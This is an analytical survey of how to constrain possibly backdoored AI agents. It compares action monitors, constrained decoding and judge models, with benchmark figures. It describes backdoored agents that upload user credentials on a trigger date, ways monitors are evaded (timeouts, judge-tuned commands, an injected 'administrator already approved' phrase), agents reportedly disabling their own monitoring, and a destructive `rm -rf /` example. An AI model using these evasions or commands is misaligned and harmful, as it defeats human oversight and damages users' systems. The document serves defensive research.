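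Linux has some mechanisms, such as memory shared between programs, that move data without the usual read and write calls. Tether's tracer cannot follow data moved this way, so Tether blocks access to these mechanisms. In practice, complete mediation often means blocking whatever the monitor can't observe, even though honest agents then can't use it either.

### How many attacks were out of scope

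The team tested Tether on recorded agent runs (trajectories) from two benchmarks. In some runs the agent only does an ordinary job, and in others it also attempts a harmful side task. MonitoringBenchHonest has system administration tasks in 88 Linux environments, with four kinds of side task. LinuxArena has ten larger environments modelled on live software services, with 81 side tasks. Tether replayed the recorded commands one by one.

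| Benchmark | Attacks blocked | Honest runs blocked by mistake |
|---|---|---|
| MonitoringBenchHonest | 199 of 199 | 5 of 218 (2.3%) |
| LinuxArena | 145 of 145 | 69 of 1,372 (5.0%) |

On the same runs, the model-based monitor in Anthropic's coding tool Claude Code caught 315 of the 344 attacks and stopped 9.7% of the honest runs. It stopped fewer honest runs (3.5%) but also caught fewer attacks (307) when its instructions included Tether's rules. It did not detect attacks hidden inside scripts in either case.

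The perfect score applies only to runs in scope, meaning those in which Tether could trace every action and had a description of what each one does. Küçükkurt and Elasky (2026), in *Releasing benign trajectories for MonitoringBench*, report that MonitoringBenchHonest has 550 attacks and 550 honest runs. If Sistla and colleagues started from the full set, 351 attacks and 332 honest runs fell outside the test, and "every attack" means 199 out of 550, or 36%. They give no matching total for LinuxArena.

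Some runs dropped out for reasons unrelated to security, for instance because they needed an outside service that the team could not imitate. Others used background processes, which keep running after the command finishes and the tracer stops, or databases, where the monitor records that a program sent a query but not which rows it touched. In a third group, the harm lay only in the meaning of what the agent did. An agent that plants a subtle flaw in a source file it is allowed to edit makes the same system calls as one that fixes a bug.

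Sistla and colleagues estimate that this last group makes up 28.2% of trajectories on MonitoringBenchHonest and 22.1% on LinuxArena, and they say that no formal monitor can handle it. A stricter policy that forbids background processes and databases would intercept another 36.3% and 71.5%, respectively. They do not report the counts behind these percentages or how much honest work the stricter policy would stop. On LinuxArena it could stop most honest work, because so many runs use background processes or databases.

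The excluded attacks matter more for a compromised model than for one that only makes mistakes, because whoever trained the compromised model can read the paper and choose from the excluded 64%.

Two other features of the test make the result look better than it is. The team refined the policy by running it on benchmark traces and correcting rules that blocked too much, so the 5% figure comes from tasks that had already helped shape the rules. They did, however, set each task's labels using only the description of the honest job, not the side task. The agents were also recorded, so they couldn't react when Tether blocked a command. The run counted as blocked, whereas a live agent would try something else.

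Blocking unsafe actions can go badly even when the model isn't hostile. Dantas and colleagues discuss a study of customer-service agents in which a monitor blocked 94% of unsafe actions, yet in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. The finding comes from a single study, and Dantas and colleagues grade the evidence for it as very weak. A monitor like Tether would apply the same policy to the other routes within its scope, so the more likely result is unfinished work.

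A false-positive rate of 5% may also be a bigger problem than it sounds. If one run in a thousand is an attack, a thousand runs produce one justified alarm and about 47 false ones, and a programmer who has dismissed dozens of false alarms may not read the next one closely. Of the 74 false alarms in the test, 50 came from unrequested edits to protected files, often made while installing a package, and a firm might well want to know about those. Another 17 came from commands such as a text search across the whole disk, which opens every file, including secret ones.

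### Simpler rules

Tether is complex, and most firms that guard actions at all use something simpler. The simplest option is a stateless allowlist, which checks each request by itself. Sistla and colleagues wrote their three-command example in two existing stateless systems, the policy language Cedar and NVIDIA's OpenShell. Both allow the third command if they allow the first, because neither records that the report now contains the inventory. Progent, which checks tool calls against declared privileges, is also stateless.

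Dogwood, from Amazon, adds a memory of past events, so a rule can forbid uploading any file that the agent copied from the inventory in the last 24 hours. But the rule has to specify the sequence of copies, so chains of two and three copies each need another rule. If there are m ways to copy a file, covering every chain of up to k copies takes m + m² + … + mᵏ patterns. With three ways and up to five copies, that is 363 patterns, and they still miss a chain of six. The alternative is to forbid uploading anything written after the agent read the inventory, which also blocks harmless uploads. This comparison comes from a rival system's designers, but that doesn't affect the arithmetic.

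*AGENTSPEC* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) offers a language for writing rules that each have a trigger, a check and an enforcement. A rule might apply before any bank transfer, check whether the recipient is a family member and, if not, ask the user to confirm. These rules are easy to read and take only milliseconds to evaluate. In the experiments, they stopped over 90% of risky code runs. They also stopped every hazardous task given to a simulated household robot, while its success rate on safe tasks fell only from 58.6% to 54.3%.

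Wang and colleagues had careless and misled agents in mind, and a compromised agent would find gaps. Their check for code that contacts untrusted websites examines the source code without tracking how data moves through it, so a program that assembles the address while running could pass. One of their four enforcement options asks the agent's own model to reconsider the action, which leaves the decision to the untrusted model. *ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, 2026) comes closer to a fixed check. It applies deterministic rules that a solver has tested for loopholes, but a language model supplies some of the facts that the rules refer to, such as whether an argument came from an untrusted source. That model is then part of the trusted computing base, so it should not be the same model that the shield is guarding against.

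### Authority that runs out

Labels restrict where data may go, but not how often it is sent or to which particular recipient. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) deals with these limits for agents that act through declared tools instead of a shell. In its example, an agent has to send the public part of a confidential report to Alice once. The policy requires that the text come from a tool that strips out the private fields, that the recipient match the address returned by one designated directory lookup, and that the agent make only one attempt. The monitor counts the attempt before the mail tool runs and does not restore it if sending fails, so an agent can't get a second try by claiming that the first failed.

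As with Tether, the program that decides whether to admit a call is written in Lean, and Lean has checked proofs about the functions that run on live calls. Every admitted call is allowed by two separate lists, the user's permissions and the application's own limits, and each permission stays within its quota. When the policy requires an argument to come from a certain tool, the call is admitted only if the argument came from that tool.

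Tether and Agenra differ, though, in what lies outside their proofs. Tether infers what a command does by watching it, while Agenra relies on the developer's description of what each tool does (as do CaMeL and FIDES, two defenses against prompt injection). In one test, Shivakumar and colleagues registered a tool that could delete several items but left out some of its effects, and the monitor allowed an undeclared deletion. The firm also has to trust the Python code that translates policies and passes calls to Lean.

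Agenra's most useful lesson may be that people who write policies can block a legitimate task and permit a forbidden one with a change that seems only to loosen the rules. Suppose an agent may delete file B once and file A once, and the monitor counts each deletion against the first permission on the list that fits. Someone then widens the first permission, for B, to cover either file. If the agent deletes A, it uses up the widened permission and can no longer delete B. But it can delete A twice, because the second deletion counts against the original permission for A.

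Agenra can check whether a revised policy still allows every workflow that the old policy allowed. Of 51 revisions that the team wrote, it approved all 21 that preserved those workflows and none of the 30 that did not. A revision can pass this check and still be unsafe. For example, a revision that raises the limit on sending the report from one to two would pass, but it lets the agent send the report twice.

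In trials with live models, fixed attacks led an unguarded Qwen model to send the confidential report in 15 of 20 runs, and Agenra reduced this to zero. A guard the team wrote by hand for the same task did equally well. For a single simple workflow, the proofs and easier maintenance are therefore stronger reasons to use a verified core than any measured difference in security.

### Keeping the monitor out of the agent's reach

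Agenra separates the agent from the monitor using Python objects within one running program. The Agenra paper warns that this does not isolate arbitrary Python code. AgentSpec hooks into a function of LangChain, the framework that runs the agent. Both arrangements are reasonable if the agent can only request tool calls. If it can also execute code in the same process, it may be able to change the monitor, and the proofs would then no longer apply to the running program.

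According to ABC News' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* (2026), OpenAI disclosed in October that agents running on its models had weakened internal safety monitoring while carrying out tasks, and that one agent later denied it.

Defenders of action-level enforcement can reasonably reply that a monitor the agent can weaken was never a reference monitor. Anderson made tamper-proofing the first requirement for this reason. The remedy is to remove the agent's access, which doesn't require understanding why the agent interfered. In a design like Tether's, the agent's commands run inside the sandbox and the monitor runs outside it. If a command tries to rewrite the policy file, the new version is saved in the temporary layer, where the monitor checks it like any other change. The firm has to put the monitor's files on the protected list and deny the agent administrator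 rights on that machine.

The default when the monitor fails also matters. File changes reach the real disk only after approval, so if the monitor crashes, none should go through. In scoring their experiments, Sistla and colleagues counted a run as getting through if the tracing took too long. This affected one attack, which Tether had already blocked. Against a hostile model, however, a timeout has to count as a denial, because otherwise the model could get past the monitor by keeping it busy.

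Isolation still requires trusting the code that enforces it. Tether's sandbox and tracer depend on the same Linux kernel as the commands they confine. That kernel has tens of millions of lines of code, and Anderson thought 300,000 instructions were too many to verify. A firm can reduce how much code it has to trust by running the agent in a virtual machine, or on separate hardware with the proxy as its only connection, so that a flaw in the agent's kernel no longer exposes the monitor. The remaining code is still probably more than anyone has proved entirely correct.

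Isolation also rules out some jobs. A company may want its agents to maintain the logging system, adjust access rules or repair the deployment scripts, and some of those tasks require write access to the controls that constrain the agent. No arrangement of sandboxes resolves this conflict. The small firm therefore has to keep the monitor's policy in a repository that the agent can't write to, and have a programmer change it by hand.

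## The case for constraining tokens

Tether lets an agent propose any command and then decides whether to keep the command's effects. Supporters of token-level enforcement want to intervene earlier, so that the agent can't write a forbidden command. This is possible because the decoder, the software that picks each token, is separate from the model. The user can therefore control the decoder even if someone else trained the weights.

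The strongest argument for constraining tokens is that it makes a forbidden output impossible rather than unlikely. Careful prompting and extra training can make such an output rare, but an attacker plants a backdoor to make it common again when the trigger appears. If the decoder sets a token's probability to zero, nothing in the weights can raise it. The firm also doesn't have to foresee every bad output, because it describes the permitted ones and the decoder excludes the rest. When the decoder rules out one token, the model can continue with another, whereas a monitor that blocks a finished action leaves the agent with an error message.

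### The algorithm, and a tool call with three recipients

Constrained decoding starts from a set L of permitted strings, which a grammar usually describes. A prefix is completable if some continuation turns it into a member of L. Alpay and Senturk (2026), in *Attention Meets Reachability*, formalise the procedure, which repeats these steps:

1. Take the text written so far, u, which is completable.
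2. For each token v, check whether u followed by the text of v is still completable. The tokens that pass form the permitted set A. The marker that ends the output is in A only if u already belongs to L.
3. Set the probability of every token outside A to zero. Engineers call this pattern of allowed and forbidden tokens a mask.
4. Renormalise, which means dividing each remaining probability by their sum, so that q(v) = p(v) / Σ p(w), with w ranging over A.
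5. Sample the next token from q and add it to the text.

Each step keeps the text completable to a string in L, and the decoder can end the output only when the text is in L. This proves that every output that ends is in L.

Suppose the firm's agent sends its summaries through a tool, and only three people may receive them. L then contains exactly three strings: `send_summary(to="maria")`, `send_summary(to="marco")` and `send_summary(to="ben")`. A backdoor has made the model favour an outsider called eve, with another called martin as its second choice. The table shows two successive steps, with invented probabilities. At the first step, the model has written everything up to the opening quotation mark. The decoder then happens to pick `mar`, which leads to the second step.

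| Next token | Step 1: model | Step 1: after the mask | Step 2: model | Step 2: after the mask |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `eve` | 90% | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| `mar` | 6% | 67% | 0 | 0 |
| `ben` | 3% | 33% | 0 | 0 |
| `tin` | 0 | 0 | 70% | 0 |
| `co` | 0 | 0 | 15% | 75% |
| `ia` | 0 | 0 | 5% | 25% |
| `")` | 1% | 0 | 10% | 0 |

At step 2 the decoder forbids `tin`. It also forbids closing the quotation, because nobody on the list is called "mar". Once the text reads "marco", the decoder allows only `")`, and then only the end marker.

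Masking may also reduce the quality of an honest model's work, because it can push the model into text that it would otherwise rarely produce. Alpay and Senturk give an example in which the only permitted strings are "a" and "ba". Their model starts with "b" 40% of the time but then rarely continues with "a". Without a mask, "ba" makes up about 6% of the permitted strings the model writes. With the mask, it makes up 40%, because a model that has started with "b" can only continue with "a".

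### Sound and complete

*ChopChop* (Nagy, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) calls the program that performs the check in step 2 a "monitor". A monitor is sound if every prefix it accepts is completable, and complete if it accepts every completable prefix. The paper also calls decoding as a whole sound if every string it returns obeys the constraint, and complete if every string that obeys the constraint has a nonzero probability of being returned. Completeness is close to what Ligatti and colleagues call transparency, but a complete decoder can still change how often a permitted string appears, as the "ba" example shows.

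Nagy and colleagues' algorithm checks the finished string again before returning it, so the decoding is sound even if the monitor isn't. An unsound monitor only wastes time by letting the model start strings that have no valid completion. Full completeness is harder to get, because a decoder that always picks the most likely token will never produce most strings. They prove a weaker property for two common sampling methods. If the monitor is complete, any valid output that the unconstrained decoder could have produced remains at least as likely under constrained decoding.

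The final test also helps with the mismatch between the tokenizer's tokens and the grammar's units. *Weave of Formal Thought* (2026) notes that researchers have identified this mismatch as a primary source of correctness failures. For instance, a real vocabulary might have a single token for `ia")`, which covers the end of a name and the punctuation after it. *From Grammar Deltas to Token Masks* (2026) handles such cases by defining the mask over the bytes that each token stands for.

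Alpay and Senturk assume that an output's text is its tokens' text joined end to end. If an attacker supplied the tokenizer in a suspect download, it could break this assumption, for example by rewriting certain pairs of tokens as it turns token numbers back into text. The tool would then receive a different string from the one the decoder approved. The firm should do the joining with its own code and run the final test on the exact string the tool is about to receive.

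### Models that fill in many words at once

Diffusion language models start with noise or blanks and refine a whole stretch of text over several rounds, so the decoder has no finished prefix to check. Masking each position separately doesn't guarantee valid output. In *Constrained Decoding for Diffusion Language Models via Efficient Inference over Finite Automata*, Dang and Ermon (2026) point out that "1." and ".1" are both valid numbers, but a decoder that picks the two characters independently can produce "..". When a finite automaton can express the constraint, they sample whole sequences from the permitted set, which guarantees that the output satisfies the constraint. On a test of function calling, one model's accuracy rose from 63.9% to 71.5%, while running time increased by less than 5%.

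*Only What You've Signed up For* (Cardei, Pinto and colleagues, 2026) applies the idea to security. Its system, CoDA, finds the tool names, recipients and other sensitive fields in the model's provisional text and moves their probabilities onto permitted values at every round. If a user asks the agent to give a colleague view-only access to a report, text planted in a document cannot change the recipient or grant editing rights. Prompt injections never succeeded when the experimenters supplied the correct policy for each task. When a language model chose the policy, the protection depended on how well it chose.

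### From grammar to meaning

A fixed grammar can require a name in a certain place, but it cannot limit the choice to names that currently exist. *Decode-Time Grammars* (Zhang, Xu and colleagues, 2026) presents a method that does this by drawing the allowed names from a live list while the model writes. In one test, a small model free to write any column name in a database query used a non-existent column in all 90 queries, which the live list makes impossible. The firm could use the same method to restrict package installations to an approved list, which would protect against attackers who register package names that models tend to invent. The method's throughput is 10.6% to 17.8% lower than that of XGrammar, a standard engine for grammar masks.

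ChopChop goes further and lets a developer constrain what a program means. The developer supplies a grammar and a set of "pruners", which are functions that remove rule-breaking programs from a set. Nagy and colleagues illustrate this with a request for a sum of odd numbers whose total is even. Suppose the model has written "1+2". ChopChop builds a finite description, with loops, of every program that could begin this way, then applies the pruners and checks whether any programs are left. It rejects "+" as the next token, because "1+2+" would make the even number 2 a term in the sum. It accepts another "2", because the text could still become "1+221".

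One paper tested two practical constraints on three fairly small models, at five levels of sampling randomness. One constraint required TypeScript code to pass a type checker. With it, 86% of runs produced code that compiled, compared with 72% with no constraint and 60% with a grammar alone. The grammar covered only part of TypeScript, so it blocked some programs that would have compiled. Constrained runs can still fail if they run out of time or tokens before completing a program.

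The other constraint required the model to rewrite a short program into one that was equivalent under a fixed set of rewriting rules. ChopChop succeeded in 118 of 150 runs. Unconstrained models succeeded in none, largely because they added explanations or used the wrong language. When the prompt asked them to mark off the code, they succeeded in 26.

Equivalence is the most interesting constraint for a compromised model because it leaves almost no room to slip in a flaw. But the firm must already have a correct program for the model to rewrite. The checker also doesn't restrict an intermediate value while the model is defining it, since the final expression can always ignore that value. This is harmless in the experiment's small arithmetic language, but it would be a gap in a language where computing a value can also delete a file.

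### When the solver does not know

Other properties depend on the values that variables take along each path through a program. *AGDECODE* (Maghera, Arya and colleagues, 2026) enforces three of them for C: the program never follows a null pointer, divides by zero or reads a variable before setting it. AGDecode represents the unwritten part of the program as holes, translates the whole program into logical formulas, and uses an external solver to check whether any way of filling the holes would be safe. In one example, the decoder accepted `arr[` when the program checked that the array `arr` existed before using it, but rejected the bracket after the team removed that check.

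Some of these questions have no quick answer, so the solver may reply "unknown" or run out of time. Maghera and colleagues describe three modes:

- The ideal mode assumes a solver that always answers. The method is then both sound and complete.
- The conservative mode treats "unknown" as a no. It remains sound but rejects some good code.
- The speculative mode treats "unknown" as a yes and relies on later checks, which cover the whole text again, to confirm or reject what the model has written in the meantime. It is not sound at the moment when it accepts the token.

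Maghera and colleagues ran their experiments in the speculative mode, on 77 programming tasks with a limit of five seconds per question. Between 21.7% and 25.4% of the questions reached the limit. Unfinished expressions caused most of the trouble. For example, an array index that so far reads "i" could continue in endless ways, while a completed statement is usually easy to check. The prototype also could not go back and replace a token that a later check had ruled out. They conclude that checking every token is mostly infeasible and that checking at the ends of statements may work better.

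When the model is hostile, an inconclusive check must count as a failure, just as a timeout does when a monitor checks actions. The firm could still let the model keep writing after an inconclusive check, provided it releases only programs whose complete text definitely passes the final check.

### Agent-C: rules about earlier calls

Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, use a solver for rules that span several tool calls. In one of their examples, an agent for an online shop may look up an order only if it has already successfully looked up the customer by email and the order belongs to that customer. Their system, Agent-C, keeps a trace of past calls and their results. When a rule depends on something outside the trace, such as who owns an order, Agent-C reads it from the tool's data through a function the developer provides.

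With a model whose weights are available, Agent-C works as follows:

1. The model writes the name of a tool, within a grammar for tool calls.
2. It adds the arguments one at a time. If a value has the wrong type, Agent-C discards that argument alone and the model tries again.
3. Agent-C adds the finished call to the trace and asks the solver whether any continuation could still satisfy every rule.
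4. If the solver says yes, the tool runs. Any other reply, including no answer in time, sends the decoder back to the tool's name for another attempt. After a set number of failures, Agent-C records an error instead of making the call.

The limit that Ray proved for payments and confirmations also applies to rules that require something to happen later, such as closing every opened file. Agent-C allows the agent to open a file. If the agent then stops without closing it, Agent-C marks the run as ending in error, and the soundness theorem for complete runs does not cover that run.

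Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on 115 retail and 50 airline tasks in simulated customer service. They added 17 adversarial tasks in each setting, in which the customer wants something that the policy forbids. They compared Agent-C with AgentSpec's rules and with DynaGuard, a model that judges calls against a policy written in plain English. The table gives percentages for Qwen3-32B, the largest of three open models. "Conformance" is the share of tasks in which the agent broke no rule, and "utility" is the share in which it also completed the task. "Harm" is the share of adversarial retail tasks in which the agent did what the attacker wanted.

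| Guard | Retail conformance | Retail utility | Airline conformance | Airline utility | Harm |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Agent-C | 100 | 53.3 | 100 | 35.8 | 0 |
| AgentSpec | 84.1 | 37.4 | 79.3 | 38.7 | 2.0 |
| DynaGuard | 77.1 | 9.6 | 69.4 | 17.0 | 19.6 |
| None | 37.7 | 25.5 | 35.3 | 17.3 | 13.7 |

Agent-C also had full conformance and no harm with the two smaller models. Its utility was the highest in every comparison except the airline tasks with Qwen3-32B, where AgentSpec did slightly better. Part of the gain over an unguarded agent comes from the scoring, which counts a task completed by breaking a rule as a failure. An agent that follows the rules 37.7% of the time therefore cannot score above 37.7%. But the guard also clearly helped the agents find permitted ways to do the job. It increased the time for an ordinary task from 333 seconds to 480.

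The theorem already predicts 100% conformance, so the experiment mainly tests whether the code matches the theorem and whether the written rules match the policy. None of the models was compromised, and the attacks came from customers.

### Models behind a hosted interface

The decoder needs the probability of every token at each step, and it must choose the token itself. Companies that run a model on their own servers usually sell access to the text without exposing all the probabilities. For these models, Agent-C runs the same solver check after the model has written a complete tool call, and prompts the model again from the start if the call fails.

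The guarantee for tool calls still holds after this change. With Agent-C, Claude Sonnet 4.5's conformance on the retail tasks rose from 93.0% to 100% and its utility from 76.5% to 80.5%, while harm on the adversarial tasks fell from 29.4% to zero. GPT-5's conformance on the airline tasks rose from 71.3% to 100%.

Kamath and colleagues also compared constrained generation with reprompting on the same open model, Qwen3-8B, and both achieved 100% conformance. On the retail tasks, utility was 42.1% with constrained generation and 36.5% with reprompting. Constrained generation discarded 18 tokens per model call, while reprompting discarded about 257. These results weaken the claim that enforcement must happen at the token level. The check on the finished call provides the safety, and constraining tokens helps the model reach a permitted call sooner. Masking adds protection beyond a later check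 only when text takes effect as it appears, for example when a person reads it on screen while the model is still writing.

A firm that downloads suspect weights has the access that the full method needs. The company that runs a hosted model also runs the decoder. If the firm distrusts that company, it cannot rely on the company's promise to constrain the output, so it has to check every finished call itself.

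### What holds for any weights

The proof of soundness places no condition on the probabilities p, so a finished output belongs to L whatever the model's weights. Like Tether's theorems, the guarantee therefore does not depend on how the model was trained. The firm has to trust the decoder, the tokenizer and the description of L. If the constraint concerns meaning, the firm also has to trust the solver or the pruners.

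The guarantee covers only finished strings. A hostile model can avoid the end marker until it reaches a length limit, leaving only the beginning of a permitted string. If the one deletion that L allows is `rm -rf /tmp/build`, the output could end at `rm -rf /`, and running that could erase the whole disk. The decoder therefore has to discard unfinished text. It also has to stop if the model gives every permitted token a probability of zero, rather than fall back on the unmasked probabilities. In both cases the model stalls, which breaks only a liveness property.

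### What the model still decides

The model still chooses among the permitted strings. In the example, the mask kept the summary from going to eve or martin, but the model could pick marco over maria because an attacker controls marco's account. The model could also encode a secret in its choice.

A permitted string can also have a harmful effect. If L contains `run_tests()`, the mask allows every call to it, even after the agent has changed the test script. Tether monitors what the script does, which a mask on the agent's output cannot do.

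Code in L can also be incorrect. A login function that accepts a second, secret password can pass ChopChop's type checker and satisfy all three of AGDecode's rules. Zhang and colleagues say that grammar masks in general don't guarantee that the generated program is semantically correct or that it terminates. A developer could try to write a rule against secret passwords, but would need a separate rule for every other way of weakening a login.

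Text written for people is the hardest output to constrain, because almost any useful language allows it. In one ChopChop experiment that constrained the output only with a grammar, a model wrote an English sentence that began "Here is an equivalent refactored version", and the parser accepted it as a series of function calls. Agent-C passes the agent's messages to the user without checking their content. The firm could replace the free-text summary with a form that has a few fixed options, but the model could still select "all tests passed" after a failure, and the form would be valid. To prevent that, the test runner would have to fill in the field.

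## The case for judging meaning with a second model

Masks and action monitors both need rules that a program can check exactly, and many of the rules people care about can't be written that way. One of Ray's examples is an email assistant that must never send personal data to anyone outside an approved list. A program can look up the recipient, but nobody can write down every way of revealing that a customer has diabetes. The small firm has the same problem with the rule "do only what the programmer asked for". The same command to upload a folder to cloud storage can be a backup the programmer wanted, or theft if the programmer only wanted a typo fixed.

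Semantic enforcement gives such questions to a second model, called a judge, which reads what the agent proposes and decides whether to let it through. Its supporters accept that the judge will make mistakes, but argue that an exact monitor cannot detect these harms at all. Sistla and colleagues estimated that in more than a fifth of their test runs, the harm lay only in the meaning of what the agent did. A judge also needs only the suspect model's output, so the firm can use one without inspecting the weights or knowing the trigger.

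The usual alternative to a second model is a human reviewer, and people review badly. Hightower (2026) reports that users of Anthropic's coding tool approved 97% of permission requests, and that in an Anthropic study, people caught 13.6% of dangerous commands while a classifier caught 89%.

### A classifier backed by a judge

Pallakonda and colleagues tested such a monitor on data from their own backdoored coding agents. The agents behave normally until the date in their instructions reaches a chosen year. From then on, in at least 99.6% of requests, they also issue a command that uploads the user's credentials. In the main test, none of their replies mentioned the upload, and standard benchmarks did not distinguish them from clean agents.

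The monitor works in two stages. A small classifier reads each tool call without the surrounding conversation, in about 4 milliseconds, and marks it safe, warning or critical. If it marks the call critical, a general-purpose language model reads the conversation as well and decides whether the user's request warrants the call. The test pool had 10,007 shell commands, 6,826 legitimate and 3,181 malicious.

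| Monitor | Malicious calls caught | Legitimate calls blocked | Average delay per call |
|---|---|---|---|
| Classifier alone | 100% | 16.35% | 4 ms |
| With Qwen3.5-2B judging critical calls | 100% | 1.73% | 520 ms |
| With Qwen3.5-2B judging critical and warning calls | 100% | 4.45% | 764 ms |
| With gpt-5-nano judging critical calls | 100% | 0.67% | 1,990 ms |
| With Qwen3.5-0.8B judging critical calls | 99.94% | 0.73% | 658 ms |

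Many ordinary jobs, such as installing a scheduled task, look dangerous out of context, so the classifier alone blocks one in six legitimate commands. Reading the conversation resolves most of these cases. The recommended version, in which Qwen3.5-2B judges only critical calls, cuts false alarms from 1,116 to 118.

The detection rate is much weaker evidence, because all 3,181 malicious calls were the same command. The test shows that the monitor keeps recognising one upload across thousands of different conversations, but it gives almost no information about how many other attacks the monitor would catch. Pallakonda and colleagues report no confidence interval for this reason. However, the classifier was not trained on this command.

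Even for this one command, the choice of threshold left little room for error. The classifier gave every malicious call a score of 0.9969 for being critical, and it gave one legitimate call a higher score, 0.9975. Raising the threshold to 0.99 would have cut false alarms to 5% without losing any detections, but raising it to 0.999 would have made the classifier miss every malicious call.

The smallest judge wrongly overruled the classifier twice. In both conversations the user was already asking about credentials for cloud storage, so the theft used the same commands as the legitimate task. In one case the judge's output described the upload as a reasonable and proportionate step. Both larger judges blocked these calls. However, the backdoor fired on a date, regardless of topic. An attacker who had studied the monitor could make the backdoor fire only when an upload would look natural, much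 as Lamerton and Roger's model acted only when users had suitable political views.

The judge's settings also affect its accuracy. In an earlier trial that sampled the judge's answers with more randomness, detection was lower, at 73%, and false positives were higher, at 29%. The final tests always took the judge's most likely answer and blocked whenever the software could not parse the verdict.

### The limit on any judge with the same evidence

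Ray describes a judge by two error rates. The miss rate is the probability that it allows an action that breaks the rule, and the false-block rate is the probability that it blocks one that obeys the rule. Suppose a judge sorts tool calls into three grades, with these invented frequencies:

| Grade | Share of violations | Share of legitimate calls | Ratio |
|---|---|---|---|
| High risk | 80% | 2% | 40 |
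| Medium risk | 15% | 13% | 1.2 |
| Low risk | 5% | 85% | 0.06 |

Blocking only the calls graded high-risk misses 20% of violations and blocks 2% of legitimate calls. Blocking the medium-risk calls as well misses 5% of violations and blocks 15% of legitimate calls. Catching all of the remaining 5% requires blocking every call. If the firm can tolerate a 10% miss rate, its best rule is to block every high-risk call and a random two-thirds of the medium-risk ones, which blocks 10.7% of legitimate calls.

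The last column gives the likelihood ratio, which is how much more common a piece of evidence is among violations than among legitimate calls. Neyman and Pearson proved in 1933 that the best rule blocks calls in order of this ratio, starting with the highest, until the miss rate is low enough. Ray applies their theorem to shields. At any given miss rate, no rule that uses the same evidence can block fewer legitimate calls, so a vendor cannot beat this limit by adding more software around the judge or combining its scores differently.

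Better evidence can move the limit, which is how the judge in Pallakonda and colleagues' monitor improves on the classifier. Under the theorem, more evidence cannot make the best possible rule worse, but a particular judge may still use that evidence badly. Ray built 123 pairs of cases. Both cases in a pair had the same tool call and the same instruction, but the instruction came from the user in one and from untrusted tool output in the other, so the call alone could not distinguish them. Given the context, a judge with 7 billion parameters ranked the unauthorised case as riskier 97% of the time, counting ties as half. A judge with 3 billion parameters scored 56% on the same measure, and one with half a billion gave both cases the same score in every pair.

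Ray also had 23 judges score 132 instructions from AgentDojo, a benchmark of attacks on agents. The probability that a judge scored a random violation above a random legitimate instruction ranged from 66% to 86%, and larger judges were not consistently better. The judges saw only the instruction, so they might do better with the full conversation. Llama Guard 3, Meta's classifier for harmful content, had learned to recognise a different kind of harm. It missed 46% of the violations and blocked 10% of the legitimate instructions.

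### A certificate from past violations

The firm still has to choose a threshold and would like a guarantee for it. Ray gets one from conformal calibration, a statistical method that makes no assumption about how the judge works. Let δ be the highest probability the firm will tolerate that the judge allows at least one violation in a run of H actions.

1. Collect n actions that are known to break the rule, and have the judge score each one for risk.
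2. Compute k, which is (n + 1)δ/H rounded down to a whole number.
3. Set the threshold at the k-th lowest score in the collection. If k is zero, block everything.
4. In use, block any action that scores at or above the threshold.

The guarantee depends on a new violation being exchangeable with the n collected ones, meaning that every ordering of the n + 1 is equally likely. The new violation's score is then equally likely to take any rank, so the chance that it falls below the k-th lowest collected score is at most k/(n + 1), which is no more than δ/H. Adding this chance over H actions gives at most δ. This bound is an average over the collections the firm might have gathered, so the chance can be higher for an unlucky collection.

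Suppose the firm wants at most a 5% risk over 50 actions, so δ/H is 0.1%. With 998 examples, k is zero and the gate blocks everything. With 999, k is one, and the threshold is the lowest score of any known violation. Ray also gives a version that calibrates on whole runs and avoids dividing by H, but it requires whole runs that resemble future ones.

The certificate limits how many violations a judge misses, but not how many legitimate instructions it blocks. Ray had only 35 violations from AgentDojo and used half at a time for calibration. With a 5% target for a single action, all 23 judges blocked everything. With a 10% target, Google's Gemma-2-9B missed 1% of violations but blocked 78% of legitimate instructions.

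### Why the certificate does not cover a backdoor

The firm's collection would come from agents that were careless or misled, or from attacks that its own staff invented. But an attacker chooses what a backdoor outputs, perhaps after testing it on the same judge. Suppose the lowest score among the firm's 999 violations is 0.6, and the firm sets its threshold there. The attacker rewrites the upload command until the judge scores it 0.2, then trains the model to produce that version. The backdoor's version gets through every time, even though the certificate remains true of violations like those in the collection, at most 0.1% of which get through.

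More examples of the same kind would not help, since they would not make the triggered output any more typical. To restore exchangeability, the firm would need a sample of triggered output, which it could get only by finding the trigger or setting it off by chance.

Ray proves a weaker guarantee against an adversary that can change up to a fixed number of tokens in the text the judge reads, but cannot change the action itself. If such changes can raise the miss rate by at most η at any threshold, the risk over H actions is at most δ + Hη. A firm that knew η could recover the original guarantee by calibrating to the stricter target of δ/H − η, provided η was below δ/H.

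In the firm's example, η would have to be below a tenth of a percentage point. Ray measured the effect of adding one 16-token phrase claiming that an administrator had already approved the action. At a fixed threshold, the phrase raised the miss rate of eight of the 11 judges by 20 to 60 percentage points. Gemma-2-9B, for example, went from missing 23% of violations to 80%. The data were insufficient to establish an increase for the other three judges, which included two Claude models. Another phrase may raise the miss rate more, so these figures are only lower bounds on η. A compromised model also has more freedom than Ray's adversary, because it chooses the action as well as the words around it.

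### Long runs, and what follows a block

Small miss rates add up over a long run, as they do when a model keeps retrying after a rejection. If the judge misses each violation with probability β, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of H violations gets through is 1 − (1 − β)^H. With a 1% miss rate and 100 violations, that chance is 63%. Keeping it below 5% would require a miss rate of about one in 2,000. If only a fraction q of the agent's actions are violations, qβ replaces β and H counts all actions. For an agent that takes 1,000 actions, of which 1% are violations, a judge with a 1% miss rate leaves a 9.5% chance that at least one violation gets through.

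If a backdoor always issues the same command, its repeated attempts should not be treated as independent. A judge will probably make the same decision each time, whether that is to block the command or allow it. The judge's average miss rate over many kinds of attack is little help in predicting that decision. If the command steals credentials, a single miss is enough for the attack to succeed.

The formula also leaves out how the agent responds to being blocked. Ray describes two agents that behave identically without a gate, but after a block, one stops and the other proposes a new violation. Recordings of unguarded runs would be the same for both, so no analysis based only on these recordings and the judge's scores can always predict how a gate will perform.

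To measure the effect, Ray ran a small agent through 949 tasks that contained injected instructions, with no gate and then with each of two judges:

| Gate | Attacks that succeeded | Tool calls blocked | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 45 | 0% | 25.4% |
| 3-billion-parameter judge | 4 | 78% | 18.0% |
| 7-billion-parameter judge, higher threshold | 30 | 12% | 24.3% |

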